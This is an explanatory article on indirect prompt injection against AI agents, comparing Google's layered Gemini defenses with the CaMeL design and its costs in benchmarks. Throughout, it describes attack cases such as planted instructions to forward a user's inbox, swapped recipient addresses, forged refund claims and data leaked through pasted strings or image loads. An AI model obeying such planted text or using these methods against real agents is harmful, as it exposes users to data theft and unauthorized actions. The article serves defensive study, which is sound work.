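# Google's layered prompt-injection defenses in Gemini compared with its CaMeL research

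## What is indirect prompt injection, and what has Google published about it?

Indirect prompt injection is an attack in which someone hides instructions in content that an AI system will read, such as an email or a web page, to redirect the system. The user is usually the victim, whereas in direct prompt injection the user supplies the malicious text. For example, a user might ask for a summary of unread mail that includes a message from the attacker. The danger is greatest for agents, which are AI systems that carry out tasks by calling tools, because an agent that follows a hidden instruction can send an email or spend money.

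In March 2025, researchers at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich published CaMeL, a design meant to prevent text planted in emails or web pages from determining any of an agent's actions. Google's product teams have described several layers of partial defenses against the same attack for Gemini, the company's family of AI models and the assistant built on them.

### How an agent comes to read an attacker's text

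A language model takes in text and produces text. Developers turn it into an agent by giving it a list of tools and connecting it to ordinary software that carries out the tool calls it writes. *Google’s Approach for Secure AI Agents* (Díaz, Kern and Olive, 2025) describes this process as a loop. The software assembles a prompt from the developer's standing instructions, the user's request and other material, such as stored memory or retrieved documents. The model produces a plan, picks a tool and fills in its parameters. The software runs the tool and returns the result to the model, which plans again. Díaz and colleagues warn that each pass through the loop gives malicious data another chance to hijack the plan, and that an injection that reaches the agent's memory can affect later, unrelated conversations.

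Shi, Lin and colleagues (2025), in *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections*, work through the case of a user who asks Gemini to summarize and categorize unread emails. On the first turn the model writes a function call that fetches the messages. On the next turn the messages enter the model's context, the attacker's among them. Shi and colleagues write the model's output on that second turn as

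`y = M(combine(x_user, d_priv, x_adv))`

where `M` is the model, `x_user` the user's request, `d_priv` the private information in the context and `x_adv` the attacker's text. The attacker controls only the last term and does not know the private information in advance. But `combine` joins all three into one input, and the attack succeeds if `y` contains a function call that sends `d_priv` out, for instance by forwarding the user's emails. Getting private data out to an attacker in this way is known as exfiltration.

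### Why models do not keep instructions and data apart

The formula doesn't mark `x_user` as instructions to follow and `x_adv` as text to read. *Post-Training Large Language Models with LLMON*, a 2026 paper, attributes this flaw to the architecture, because a model processes every token (a word or piece of a word) through the same attention mechanism, with no built-in distinction between instructions and data. David C makes a similar point in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, writing that inside the model there is only ever a "next token" to predict.

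Developers try to add the missing distinction by labeling each part of the prompt as system instructions, user message or tool output, and training the model to give the first two priority over the third. This ranking, called the "instruction hierarchy", is a training objective and "not an architectural guarantee", according to *Eight in Ten LLMs Leak System-Prompt Secrets* (2026). *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) similarly describes delimiters, role labels and written warnings as useful engineering that creates no hard security boundary.

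*Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) provides some direct evidence of what goes wrong. The researchers wrapped identical passages of ordinary web text in different role labels and trained a simple classifier to identify the label from the model's internal activity. Because the passages were the same, the classifier could learn only the effect of the label. They then gave four models real user messages mislabeled as tool output. The classifier put the probability of "user" at 76 to 88 percent and that of "tool" never above 20 percent, although it should have reported tool output if the models had relied on the labels. The same measure predicted whether real attacks succeeded. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak a file, the researchers kept the command fixed and varied only its framing. The attack succeeded 2 percent of the time in the group where the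 command registered least as user text and 70 percent of the time in the group where it registered most.

None of the four models was Gemini, and the largest had about 120 billion parameters, so the result applies to Google's products only by analogy. It does fit Shi and colleagues' finding that models better at following instructions were sometimes easier to attack, since an injected command is also an instruction.

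### Sending Bob a document

The CaMeL paper explains its design with a small office task, which Willison (2025) reproduces in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. A user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested in their last meeting, and adds that Bob's email address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The assistant has to find the notes, extract the name and address, fetch the document from the user's drive and send it.

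An attacker who can edit the notes could add a sentence telling the assistant to also forward the user's inbox to an outside address. The attacker could instead replace Bob's address with their own, without adding any instruction. The assistant would then perform every step the user asked for, in the right order, but send the document to the attacker.

*Control flow* means which actions an agent takes, in what order and under what conditions. *Data flow* means which information reaches which actions. The added sentence attacks the control flow because it introduces a step the user never requested. The changed address corrupts only the data flow. The agent still performs the "send" step the user requested, but the attacker has chosen the recipient.

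If the assistant fixes its list of steps before it opens the notes, the extra sentence can no longer add a step. This stops the first attack but not the second, because the address still has to come from the notes. CaMeL therefore also tracks where each value came from and checks it before the assistant sends the email. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) says CaMeL protects against both attacks.

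Defenses that look for suspicious text have a similar blind spot, because an email address planted in a set of notes looks like any other. *Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026), a study done at Amazon, measured this problem in 90 simulated cases. In one, an agent must settle a claim over a damaged item. The order record authorizes a refund of $899.99, but the buyer, who is the attacker, wants $1,074.99. The buyer can either demand the larger sum or falsely state that it is the authorized total. Averaged over five models, none of them Gemini, demands of this kind succeeded in 15.0 percent of runs and false statements about the current facts in 18.6 percent. A defense that detects and removes injected text cut the success rate of demands to 2.4 percent, but that of false statements only to 12.1 percent. Another defense, which checks tool calls against a policy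 written for the task, lowered the overall success rate only from 17.0 to 15.4 percent, because the tampered call generally used a tool that the task needed anyway.

Whether the changed address counts as prompt injection depends on the definition. The usual definitions exclude it because it contains no instruction. Zhang and colleagues would instead call planted content an injection when it tries to influence a decision that its source has no authority to determine. Bob's address is hard to classify even under that definition, because the user named the notes as the place to find it, and Zhang and colleagues class a falsehood from an authorized source as misinformation. The CaMeL paper treats the example as a prompt injection risk. That classification is more useful for comparing defenses, because the document goes to the wrong address whatever the attack is called.

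### Making an attack unlikely, or ruling it out

Willison coined the term "prompt injection" by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent SQL injection with parameterized queries, which ensure that the database never interprets the user's text as a command. David C argues that language models have no equivalent protection and may never get one, so developers should aim to reduce the likelihood and impact of attacks and rely more on safeguards outside the model that limit what the system can do.

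Defenses against indirect prompt injection fall into two families. A *probabilistic* defense relies on a model's judgment and lowers the share of attacks that succeed. Examples include training a model on sample attacks and scanning incoming email with a classifier. A *deterministic* defense applies fixed rules in software. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) places CaMeL in the deterministic family, which aims to keep agents from making decisions based on untrusted data. The strictest form of this standard, set out in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025), requires that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, it must be "impossible" for that input to trigger a consequential action.

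The difference matters because attackers can try again. Willison calls 99 percent detection a failing grade in application security. If a filter misses one attack in a hundred and each attempt is independent, the chance that at least one of 100 attempts gets through is 1 − 0.99^100, or about 63 percent. Attackers can also adapt their attacks. Shi and colleagues found that small adjustments could defeat many defenses that had done well against a fixed set of examples.

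Repeated attacks don't weaken a fixed rule, but the rule covers only what its author wrote into it. Díaz and colleagues give the example of a policy engine, software outside the model that checks each action before it runs, which blocks any purchase over $500 and asks the user to confirm those between $100 and $500. No injected text, however persuasive, will get a $600 purchase past that rule. But a $90 purchase goes straight through, and whether a $300 one is stopped depends on how carefully the user reads the confirmation request. Rules also handle context poorly. Sending an email after reading a document may be what the user wanted, or it may be data theft. Model-based defenses can take context into account, but they fail unpredictably and offer no guarantee. Díaz and colleagues conclude that neither kind of defense is sufficient alone. Google combines them, an approach security engineers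 call defense in depth, in which one imperfect defense may stop what another misses.

*AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026) argues that when the same words can be either legitimate or an attack depending on context, no fixed policy can prevent every attack without also blocking some legitimate actions. For example, someone emails to request a travel refund and adds that the department head has approved it. The agent should act on that claim if it is true, but if it is false, the email is an attack. A rule that disregards all such claims will block honest refunds, and a rule that accepts them will pay dishonest ones. Two of Meta's injection detectors could not reliably tell such emails apart. They were tested on 4,200 pairs that differed only in a clause claiming some authority, and scored between 0.43 and 0.59 on a scale where 0.5 is guessing.

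The argument is informal, and it still leaves some attacks that software can rule out by construction. For example, software can block any step that the user's request did not call for, without knowing whether anything in the notes is true. It can't block false addresses the same way, so it has to rely on something it can check, such as whether the recipient is already on a trusted list, or ask the user.

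### The Google documents

Seven documents carry most of what Google has published on the two approaches.

- **March 2025:** *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, the CaMeL paper, is academic research, which Zhang and colleagues cite from the proceedings of a 2026 IEEE conference.
- **May 2025:** The Gemini robustness report, by Shi and colleagues, is a Google DeepMind technical report on attacks and defenses tested against Gemini models.
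- **May 2025:** The agent security paper, by Díaz and colleagues, is a white paper setting out principles for people who build or oversee agents.
- **June 2025:** The layered-defense post, Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), is a security team's blog post about protections in the Gemini app and in Google Workspace, the company's office software.
- **December 2025:** The Chrome post, Parker's *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (2025), is a security team's blog post about the design of the browser's agent.
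- **April 2026:** The Workspace update, Gavish's *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (2026), is a blog post about how Google finds new attacks and revises its defenses.
- **August 2026:** The Chrome Enterprise post, Berschadski's *Future Mode Part 2* (2026), is a product blog post for business customers.

The CaMeL paper and the robustness report are better evidence than the four blog posts because they rest on experiments, while the posts describe defenses without giving an attack success rate for any of them. The groups that wrote these documents overlap. Four of CaMeL's ten authors (Chongyang Shi, Jamie Hayes, Ilia Shumailov and Andreas Terzis) also co-wrote the robustness report, and a fifth, Christoph Kern, co-wrote the agent security paper.

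CaMeL and the layered defenses have different aims. In a passage that Willison quotes, the CaMeL paper offers "strong guarantees against unintended actions and data exfiltration", though it also states that prompt injection is not fully solved. The layered-defense post promises to make attacks harder and more expensive, and Gavish writes that indirect prompt injection is not the kind of problem "you 'solve' and move on". The two lines of work overlap in Chrome, where Parker and later Berschadski name CaMeL as a partial inspiration for one component of the browser's agent.

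## How does CaMeL keep injected text from steering an agent?

CaMeL builds on an earlier proposal to divide an agent's work between two language models, one that plans and calls tools and one that reads untrusted text. The CaMeL paper describes an attack that this division does not stop. CaMeL keeps the division and adds software that tracks where each piece of data came from and checks the data before the agent acts.

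### The dual-LLM pattern

Willison (2023) made the earlier proposal in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*. He assumes that a model may obey an injected instruction and tries to limit the resulting harm. A *privileged model* receives the user's request and can call tools but never sees untrusted content, which is read by a *quarantined model* that cannot call tools. The controller, which is ordinary software, runs the tools, passes text to the quarantined model and displays results to the user.

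The controller stores the quarantined model's output under a name and shows the privileged model only that name. Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest email. The privileged model requests the email, and the controller fetches it and stores it as `$VAR1`. The privileged model then requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller gives the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as `$VAR2`. The privileged model writes a reply containing `$VAR2`, and the controller substitutes the summary when it displays the reply. If the email contains a hidden instruction to delete the user's mail, only the quarantined model reads it, and that model cannot delete anything.

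Willison allowed an exception when the quarantined model only has to sort a text into one of a few fixed categories. The controller can check that the answer is one of those categories and pass it on, since a fixed category name cannot contain a new instruction.

Willison nevertheless called the solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single programming mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model undoes the protection. The pattern also had a flaw that, as Willison wrote in 2025, was not known until the CaMeL paper.

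### A safe plan with the wrong address

The task of sending Bob his document shows the flaw. The privileged model can plan this task without reading the meeting notes, but the quarantined model has to extract Bob's address from them. An attacker can change the address in the notes or add an instruction telling the quarantined model to return a different one. In either case, the controller stores the attacker's address in the variable meant for Bob's.

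The privileged model then calls the email tool with that name as the recipient. As *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* explains for a similar case, the software fills in the actual address only when the call runs. The isolation that protects the plan also hides the data from the privileged model, so it cannot detect that the address is wrong.

According to a passage of the CaMeL paper that Willison quotes, the dual-LLM pattern keeps an attacker from calling arbitrary tools but "does not completely eliminate all prompt injection risks". The pattern protects the control flow but not the data flow.

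### What CaMeL adds

CaMeL, short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning", keeps the privileged and quarantined models but replaces the controller with an interpreter, a program that executes other programs.

The privileged model receives the user's request and a description of the available tools. It writes a plan for the whole task as a program, rather than calling tools one at a time. The program is in a restricted version of Python, which the researchers chose because models already write Python well. The restrictions rule out constructs such as arbitrary `while` loops, according to *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026), which extends CaMeL to check plans before they run. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) examined CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, banking, travel and messaging tasks. On average, a plan had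 about 52 lines, five tool calls and four branches.

CaMeL's planner writes the whole program before any tool has returned output, so it can't look at a search result and work out its layout, as an ordinary agent can. Developers therefore have to describe the format of every tool's output beforehand. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) found this when they built their own version, described in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*

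Microsoft's FIDES, a related system, avoids some of this difficulty by planning one step at a time, whereas CaMeL plans every step at the start. The FIDES planner sees which steps have already run but not the values they returned.

CaMeL's interpreter executes the program and is the only component that calls tools. It was built to record where each value came from, which a standard Python interpreter running the same code would not do.

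When the program needs information from untrusted text, it calls the quarantined model like a function, passing it a question, the text and the format of the answer, such as an email address. The interpreter stores the answer in a variable and doesn't pass it to the privileged model. Extracting an address is easier than writing a plan, so the CaMeL paper suggests using a smaller model, possibly on the user's own machine. The company hosting the privileged model would then receive the user's request but none of the private data that the tools return.

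Each value carries *capabilities*, which are tags recording where the value came from and who may read it. In an example from Nikolaou and colleagues, a calendar event may be read by the user and the people invited, and its description counts as trusted only if the user wrote it. When the program computes one value from another, the interpreter keeps track of the connection, so an address extracted from an email is as untrusted as the email.

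Before each tool call, the interpreter applies a *security policy*, a rule that allows or blocks the call based on the tool, its arguments and their capabilities. CaMeL's policies are short Python functions. One policy for the banking tasks in AgentDojo allows a password change if the new password came from a trusted source. Otherwise, it blocks the change and gives the reason that the password does not come from the user. Willison describes a third possible outcome for emails to unknown addresses, asking the user.

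CaMeL checks policies while the program is running because some of the facts they depend on are not available earlier. Nikolaou and colleagues tried to restate CaMeL's 28 policies for AgentDojo as rules that software could check against the plan alone, and succeeded with 22. The other six depended on facts such as who had access to a shared file when the call was made. Because CaMeL checks each call separately, a policy cannot easily express a requirement about the whole task, for example that the agent must close every incident ticket it opens.

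If a program fails, perhaps because the privileged model misjudged a format, CaMeL has that model write a new one using the error message. This is a weak point in the isolation because an error message may depend on untrusted data, so CaMeL censors the messages to limit the risk. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) note in *The LLMbda Calculus* that this retry loop runs outside the interpreter's tracking and that the censoring has no formal guarantee.

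### Bob's document, step by step

For the request to send Bob his document, the privileged model might write a program like this simplified one:

```
notes    = find_meeting_notes()
doc_name = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob request?",
                           notes, format=Text)
address  = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?",
                           notes, format=EmailAddress)
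document = fetch_from_drive(doc_name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

The attacker has added a sentence to the notes telling the assistant to forward the user's inbox to an outside address. The interpreter runs the first line and stores the notes, including that sentence, in `notes`. The privileged model has already finished its work and never reads the notes.

On the next two lines, the quarantined model does read the sentence. Even if it follows the injected instruction, it has no email tool and can only write an answer. If it answers the question about the address with a paragraph about forwarding mail, the answer does not fit the required format and the step fails. If it gives the same paragraph as the document's name, the interpreter searches the drive for a file with that name and presumably finds none. The attacker may have spoiled the user's task, but the inbox isn't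 forwarded, because no line of the program does that.

This time the attacker has replaced Bob's address in the notes with their own. Every line runs as planned, and the quarantined model correctly returns the attacker's address. The plan offers no protection because it sends the email to whatever address is in the notes.

The interpreter has recorded that `address` came from the meeting notes, however, and it applies a policy before running the last line. A policy based on the rule in Willison's description would look roughly like this:

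```
def check_send_email(to, attachment):
    if came_from_user(to) or to in trusted_contacts:
        return Allowed
    return AskUser("Send this file to an unknown address?")
```

The user didn't type the attacker's address, and it is not among the trusted contacts, so the interpreter stops and shows the user the request. If the user refuses, the document stays in the drive.

Bob's real address also comes from the notes and carries the same tag, so the tag alone could not have separated the two cases. The policy lets an untampered request through only because Bob is on the list of contacts. If Bob were a new client, the user would get the same question about his correct address as about the attacker's, and would have to tell the two apart.

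The question therefore has to show the exact address and file. A user who has just asked for an email will probably agree if the question is only "Send the email?" *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) proved a related result for simpler agents that need approval before sending a message. If the approval covers whatever message the agent sends next, an injected instruction can use it to send private data. If it covers only the exact message the user approved, an attacker who reads the agent's messages learns nothing extra, although one who can also observe their timing may learn a little.

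The policy determines which attacks CaMeL stops. Foerster and colleagues describe policies that use the other half of the tag, the list of people who may read a value, to stop the agent from sending a confidential document to someone without access. The table compares that rule with the one based on trusted contacts. "Stops" means that the interpreter blocks the email or asks the user.

| What is in the notes | Only trusted contacts may receive email | Only people with access may receive the file |
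|---|---|---|
| Bob's real address; Bob is a contact but has no access to the file yet | Sends | Stops |
| The address of an outsider | Stops | Stops |
| Bob's real address, but the name of a confidential file | Sends | Stops |
| The address of a colleague who is a contact and has access to the file | Sends | Sends |

The access rule catches the swapped file, which the contacts rule misses. It also interrupts the honest request, since people often ask for a document because they don't have access to it. Neither rule catches the last case, where the document goes to the wrong colleague. Someone has to decide which rule fits, and CaMeL then enforces it.

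### What the design guarantees

Peters-Gill and colleagues define this guarantee formally. A control-flow plan is a program, fixed in advance, that determines which tools the agent calls and in what order, given the results of earlier steps. An agent has *control-flow integrity* if it can only follow such a plan and the plan depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions. An agent is "CaMeL-secure" under a set of policies if it has control-flow integrity and the system enforces those policies on every tool call.

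CaMeL maintains control-flow integrity by having the privileged model write the program before any tool returns output, so an attacker's text cannot influence the program. The interpreter then runs only that program. This part of the guarantee needs no policies and holds even if the attacker fully controls the quarantined model.

It does not mean that untrusted data has no effect on what the agent does. A program can contain a branch that depends on the notes:

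```
if ask_quarantined("Is Bob's request urgent?", notes, format=YesNo):
    send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
else:
    save_draft(to=address, attachment=document)
```

An attacker who edits the notes can decide whether the email goes out at once or waits as a draft, but cannot make the agent do anything else. Control-flow integrity limits the agent to the paths in the program, so it gives more protection when the program has fewer paths.

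Garby and colleagues found an extreme case when running CaMeL with its policies switched off. One banking task in AgentDojo tells the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it. Those instructions were not available to the planner in advance, so it wrote a loop that read each one and had a branch for every tool. An attacker who controlled the file could then call any tool without making the agent depart from its program, and in two runs the attack succeeded. Foerster and colleagues therefore state that the guarantee holds only if the planner does not let the quarantined model determine parts of the control flow. They also note that tasks whose steps are listed in untrusted data do not suit this kind of design.

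CaMeL's protection of data flow depends on its policies. Garby and colleagues sorted the 144 combinations of user task and attack in AgentDojo's banking tasks into two groups. In 97 of them, the attack needs a tool call or file access that would not normally appear in the program for the user's task. For example, an attacker can't get an agent to send money if the user only asked for a summary of recent transactions. Writing the program first is generally enough to stop these attacks. In the other 47, the user's own task could include the steps the attacker needs, so stopping the attack depends on the policies. The proportions would differ for other tasks, but a third is a large share to depend on someone writing the policies correctly.

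Policies also depend on accurate tags. The quarantined model's answer can depend on everything in the question it receives, and Dongol models this by letting the attacker choose the answer freely, using any secrets the question contains. Suppose a program gives the quarantined model both an incoming email and the user's account number, then sends its answer to the email's author. The answer could contain the account number in a disguised form. To catch this, the interpreter has to tag the answer as derived from both inputs, regardless of its apparent content.

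No one has proved that CaMeL's interpreter always gets the tags right. Garby and colleagues point out this gap and note that the CaMeL paper called formal treatment a "crucial direction" for further work. They also found some cases in which the interpreter fails to track where a value came from. These are implementation faults that a better interpreter could correct without changing the design.

*Noninterference*, a stronger guarantee that is possible in theory, requires that changing one kind of input has no effect on another kind of output. For example, changing the untrusted notes could not change any trusted action. CaMeL does not offer this guarantee, and a strict version would be impractical for requests like Bob's, where the agent is supposed to send the document to whatever address the notes contain. Dongol makes the same objection about secrecy, using the example of an assistant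 that answers meeting requests from anyone by sending the user's availability. Strict noninterference would prevent the assistant from answering, even though answering is its purpose.

Dongol instead compares the agent with an imaginary one that runs the same plan under the same checks but never obeys untrusted content. The agent is secure in this relative sense if an attacker can learn from it only what they could also learn from the imaginary one. An attacker who tricks the agent into revealing the user's availability gains nothing, because an ordinary meeting request would have produced the same reply. If the trick also makes the agent include a password reset code, that is a real leak. The comparison covers only information leaks, so a false payment or a deleted file would not count as a failure.

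### False summaries

CaMeL does not guarantee that what the quarantined model writes is true. If the user asks for a summary of an email, the program has the quarantined model summarize it and then displays the result. An attacker who wrote the email can include an instruction to leave out a deadline or to report that the sender's bank details have changed. The interpreter still runs both steps as planned and correctly tags the summary as coming from an untrusted email. An accurate summary would have the same tag, so blocking summaries with that tag would block the accurate ones too.

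The same applies to text that the agent sends to other people. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* gives the example of a user who wants today's schedule emailed to a manager. The program fixes the recipient, so a planted calendar entry cannot redirect the email, but it can change what the email says about the user's day. A policy could require the agent to show the user any message based on untrusted text, but the user would still have to notice the error.

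A false summary can also lead the user to do what the agent cannot. In an example Willison gave for the dual-LLM pattern in 2023, an attacker uses injected text to make the quarantined model encode private data as a seemingly meaningless string and tell the user to paste it into a certain website to see a funny picture. The user sends the data, so the agent makes no forbidden tool call. Links and images in the displayed text are also dangerous, since loading an image from an attacker's server can send private data in the request. An assistant has to restrict them separately or treat displaying them as an action that needs a policy.

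### Why CaMeL does not have to recognize an attack

In the first trace of Bob's request, the forwarding instruction failed because the program had no forwarding step. In the second, the policy compared an address with a list. No component in either trace decided whether the notes contained an attack, so the interpreter would have treated an honest mistake in the notes, such as an old address for Bob, in the same way.

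An attacker can try to get past a classifier or a specially trained model by rewording an instruction. The main difference with CaMeL is that rewording does not help against its tags, because the interpreter assigns them according to where a text came from. A polite request, a threat and a string of characters chosen by an optimization program all get the same tag if they arrive in the same email. Willison regards this as the design's best feature, since most other proposals had tried to protect one AI model with another.

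CaMeL resembles the parameterized queries that protect databases against SQL injection. The privileged model's program corresponds to the database command, and everything from the notes enters only as data. CaMeL separates instructions from data in the software around the language models, which still make no firm distinction between the two.

CaMeL relies on correctly separating trusted sources from untrusted ones. According to Nikolaou and colleagues, it trusts the user's request, the developer's instructions and the output of some tools. If a user copies text from a malicious web page into the request, the privileged model treats the attacker's words as the user's own and may write a harmful program. The policies still apply to that program, and some may stop it. But a pasted address counts as coming from the user, so the policy in the example above would allow the email.

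## What does CaMeL cost, and which attacks does it leave open?

CaMeL lets few attacks through in published tests, but agents running it complete fewer tasks and use more tokens. Much of the evidence comes from researchers who compared CaMeL with their own defenses and had less reason to tune it.

Many of them used AgentDojo, which combines 97 user tasks with a set of attacker goals to make 949 test cases. They report *utility*, the share of tasks the agent completes correctly, and the *attack success rate*, the share of test cases in which the attack achieves its goal.

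### Fewer completed tasks

Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues could not fully reproduce CaMeL's results, so they repeat the published ones in *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025). In those results, CaMeL with GPT-4o completed 53.6 percent of AgentDojo's tasks and stopped every attack. In the team's own runs, GPT-4o without a defense completed 83.0 percent of the tasks, and 57.7 percent of attacks succeeded.

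Two later studies ran CaMeL. *AutoDojo* (2026), a benchmark that generates new attacks, tests three hosted models on three of AgentDojo's four task groups. *CapLite* (Xu, Liu and Nakayama, 2026) tests 15 open-weight models, 13 of which have 12 billion parameters or fewer. The table gives utility without attacks.

| Model | Source | Without CaMeL | With CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | Bhagwatkar and colleagues | 83.0% | 53.6% (as published) |
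| GPT-4o-mini | *AutoDojo* | 66.7% | 26.3% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | *AutoDojo* | 77.2% | 52.6% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | *AutoDojo* | 63.2% | 28.1% |
| 15 open-weight models, average | Xu and colleagues | 59.4% | 24.9% |

The losses range from about 25 to 40 percentage points. In return, CaMeL stopped almost all attacks. On Gemini 2.5 Flash, AgentDojo's standard attacks succeeded 50.4 percent of the time without a defense and 0.3 percent with CaMeL, and *AutoDojo*'s generated attacks succeeded no more often against CaMeL. Xu and colleagues counted 2,322 successes in 13,935 attacks on undefended agents, and 20 successes against agents using CaMeL, 17 of them on one model, LFM2.5-2.6B.

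Some of this security comes from agents that did nothing, since an agent that sends no messages cannot send one to an attacker. With Granite-4.2-8B, CaMeL had no program to run in 68 percent of episodes because the model returned no code, and no attack succeeded. Across all 15 models, CaMeL carried out at least one action that changes something, such as sending a message, in only 26.2 percent of the episodes with an attack.

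*MetaPermit* (2026) examines 5,581 test cases in which CaMeL stopped the attack but left the user's task unfinished. In 4,706 of them, the agent made at most two tool calls and then ended with a message, often just the bill or the list of emails it had retrieved. Some models described the tool calls they planned to make instead of writing a program that made them. These are failures to use CaMeL's unusual format, which a model with more practice might avoid, but other failures follow from CaMeL's design.

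### Planning without seeing the data

CaMeL's planner needs documentation of each tool's output format, which AgentDojo's tool descriptions lack. Peters-Gill and colleagues added the formats to every description and report that the original CaMeL evaluation required the same change. They consider this a small job that a developer does once for each set of tools.

Documentation does not help when a result calls for a step that the planner did not foresee. If the meeting notes say that Bob's document has moved to a shared folder, an ordinary agent would look there, but CaMeL will do so only if its program already has a branch for that case. Peters-Gill and colleagues trace most of the failed tasks in their tests to plans fixed too early. In some runs on AssetOpsBench, a benchmark about managing industrial equipment, one agent asked another for data on a particular machine or period and got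 data for a similar one. The program had no check for this and continued with the wrong data.

CaMeL also handles tasks poorly when their steps are in untrusted data, such as registering for an event by following the instructions on its web page. It prevents outside text from adding steps, whether the text is malicious or helpful. Foerster and colleagues call this a fundamental limitation, because a planner that read the instructions would no longer be isolated from them.

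*AgentDyn* (2026) tests this weakness. Its 60 open-ended tasks average 7.1 steps across about three applications, and all of them require the agent to revise its plan and use helpful instructions from third parties. Utility dropped severely for CaMeL and two other defenses that depend on an initial plan. A good score on AgentDojo, where most plans are short, may therefore not carry over to less predictable work. *AgentDyn* contains only tasks that require these changes of plan, so it does not measure how common they are in real use.

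### What the policies cost and what they buy

CaMeL's security policies reduce utility further because they can block a step the planner wrote correctly. Garby and colleagues measured this by running CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks with and without the policies. They used two models, GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5, and ran each task three times.

| | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Tasks completed, policies off | 32 of 48 (66.7%) | 34 of 48 (70.8%) |
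| Tasks completed, policies on | 18 of 48 (37.5%) | 18 of 48 (37.5%) |
| Successful attacks, policies off | 1 of 240 | 4 of 382 |
| Successful attacks, policies on | 0 of 231 | 0 of 357 |

The attack totals differ because not every run finished. The utility figures come from only 16 tasks, so they have a margin of error of up to 27 points either way, but utility fell by almost half on both models. Garby and colleagues also cite a test by the developers of TypeGuard, a similar system. In that test, CaMeL with its policies completed 7 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks.

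The policies block so many tasks because ordinary requests often depend on untrusted data. A user who asks an agent to pay a bill wants it to use the amount and account number on the bill, but a strict policy blocks a payment that relies on them. In a product, the agent could ask the user to approve the payment, but a benchmark has no user to answer, so the task fails. A deployed CaMeL would therefore probably complete more tasks than these figures suggest, though it would interrupt the user more often. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, warn that people who see too many approval requests start approving them without reading. They propose keeping the strictest checks for actions that are irreversible or visible to outsiders, such as wire transfers.

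In the banking tests, the policies cut the number of completed tasks by almost half and stopped attacks that would otherwise have succeeded in less than 1 percent of runs. The benefit looks small next to that loss because AgentDojo's standard attack is a fixed message telling the agent to do something else first, and a plan written in advance already stops that kind of attack. The policies are meant to catch subtler changes, such as a swapped address in the meeting notes.

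Xu and colleagues tested something closer to that case by planting a false record that matched the user's description of the item they wanted, so that an agent might act on it instead of the real one. The attack succeeded in 49 of 104 attempts on undefended agents and in 2 of 104 on agents using CaMeL with its policies. They did not repeat the test with the policies off, so it's unclear how much of the difference came from the policies, the fixed plan, or agents failing to act.

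It may be possible to keep the checks and lose less utility. Garby and colleagues built RANDORI, an agent whose planner can approve in advance the use of a particular untrusted value for a particular action. For example, a planner asked to pay a bill could approve the account number on it before anything has read the bill. With GPT-5.2, RANDORI completed 36 of 48 tasks, twice as many as CaMeL with its policies on. Across three models, 2 of 1,296 attacks on RANDORI succeeded. RANDORI enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, so looser rules may explain part of the difference in completed tasks. Its planner also decides which data to trust, and software cannot guarantee that the decision is right.

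Both successful attacks on RANDORI exploited the same task, in which the user tells the agent to make a payment as described in a file. The attacker had replaced the file with a different payment request. The user has told the agent to obey the file, so the system has no record of any other intention to check the payment against. According to Garby and colleagues, one of the two successful attacks in the CaMeL paper's evaluation was also of this kind, and that paper places it outside the threats CaMeL is meant to stop. The other was a scoring error. The agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, which triggered the benchmark's test for a successful attack.

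Someone also has to write the policies. Foerster and colleagues note that they can't be derived automatically, and that users differ in what they are willing to share. Tallam and Miller, who work at a security company, expect organizations with hundreds of tools to end up with duplicated and inconsistent rules, but offer no measurements to support this.

A policy may also stop a task only after the agent has done most of the work. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of an agent that investigates a security alert and then disconnects the affected computer, an action that needs approval from another team. If the plan has no approval step, CaMeL detects the omission only at the last call. CaMeLoT detects it before the program runs and sends the planner a description of the path that breaks the rule, so the planner can add the missing step. The check includes paths the program could never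 take, so it sometimes rejects a safe plan.

### Tokens and time

Bhagwatkar and colleagues report that with GPT-4o, CaMeL needed 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent for the median AgentDojo task. The medians in their table give lower ratios, about 1.8 and 2.2. The means give higher ones, about 3.6 and 6.1, because some tasks used far more tokens than others. The extra token use is therefore hard to state as one number, and a developer would have to plan for tasks that use many tokens as well as typical ones.

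On the smaller models that Xu and colleagues tested, CaMeL averaged 93.7 thousand tokens per episode, against 28.0 thousand without a defense. This was mainly because programs failed, and a weak model could still lack a working one after as many as ten rounds of repair. Xu and colleagues' own defense, CapLite, has the model fill in a simple list of actions instead of writing a program. It completed about as many tasks under attack as CaMeL (29.0 percent against 27.2) with 17.1 thousand tokens. But the list cannot contain loops or branches, and CaMeL did better on two Gemma models that wrote its programs reliably.

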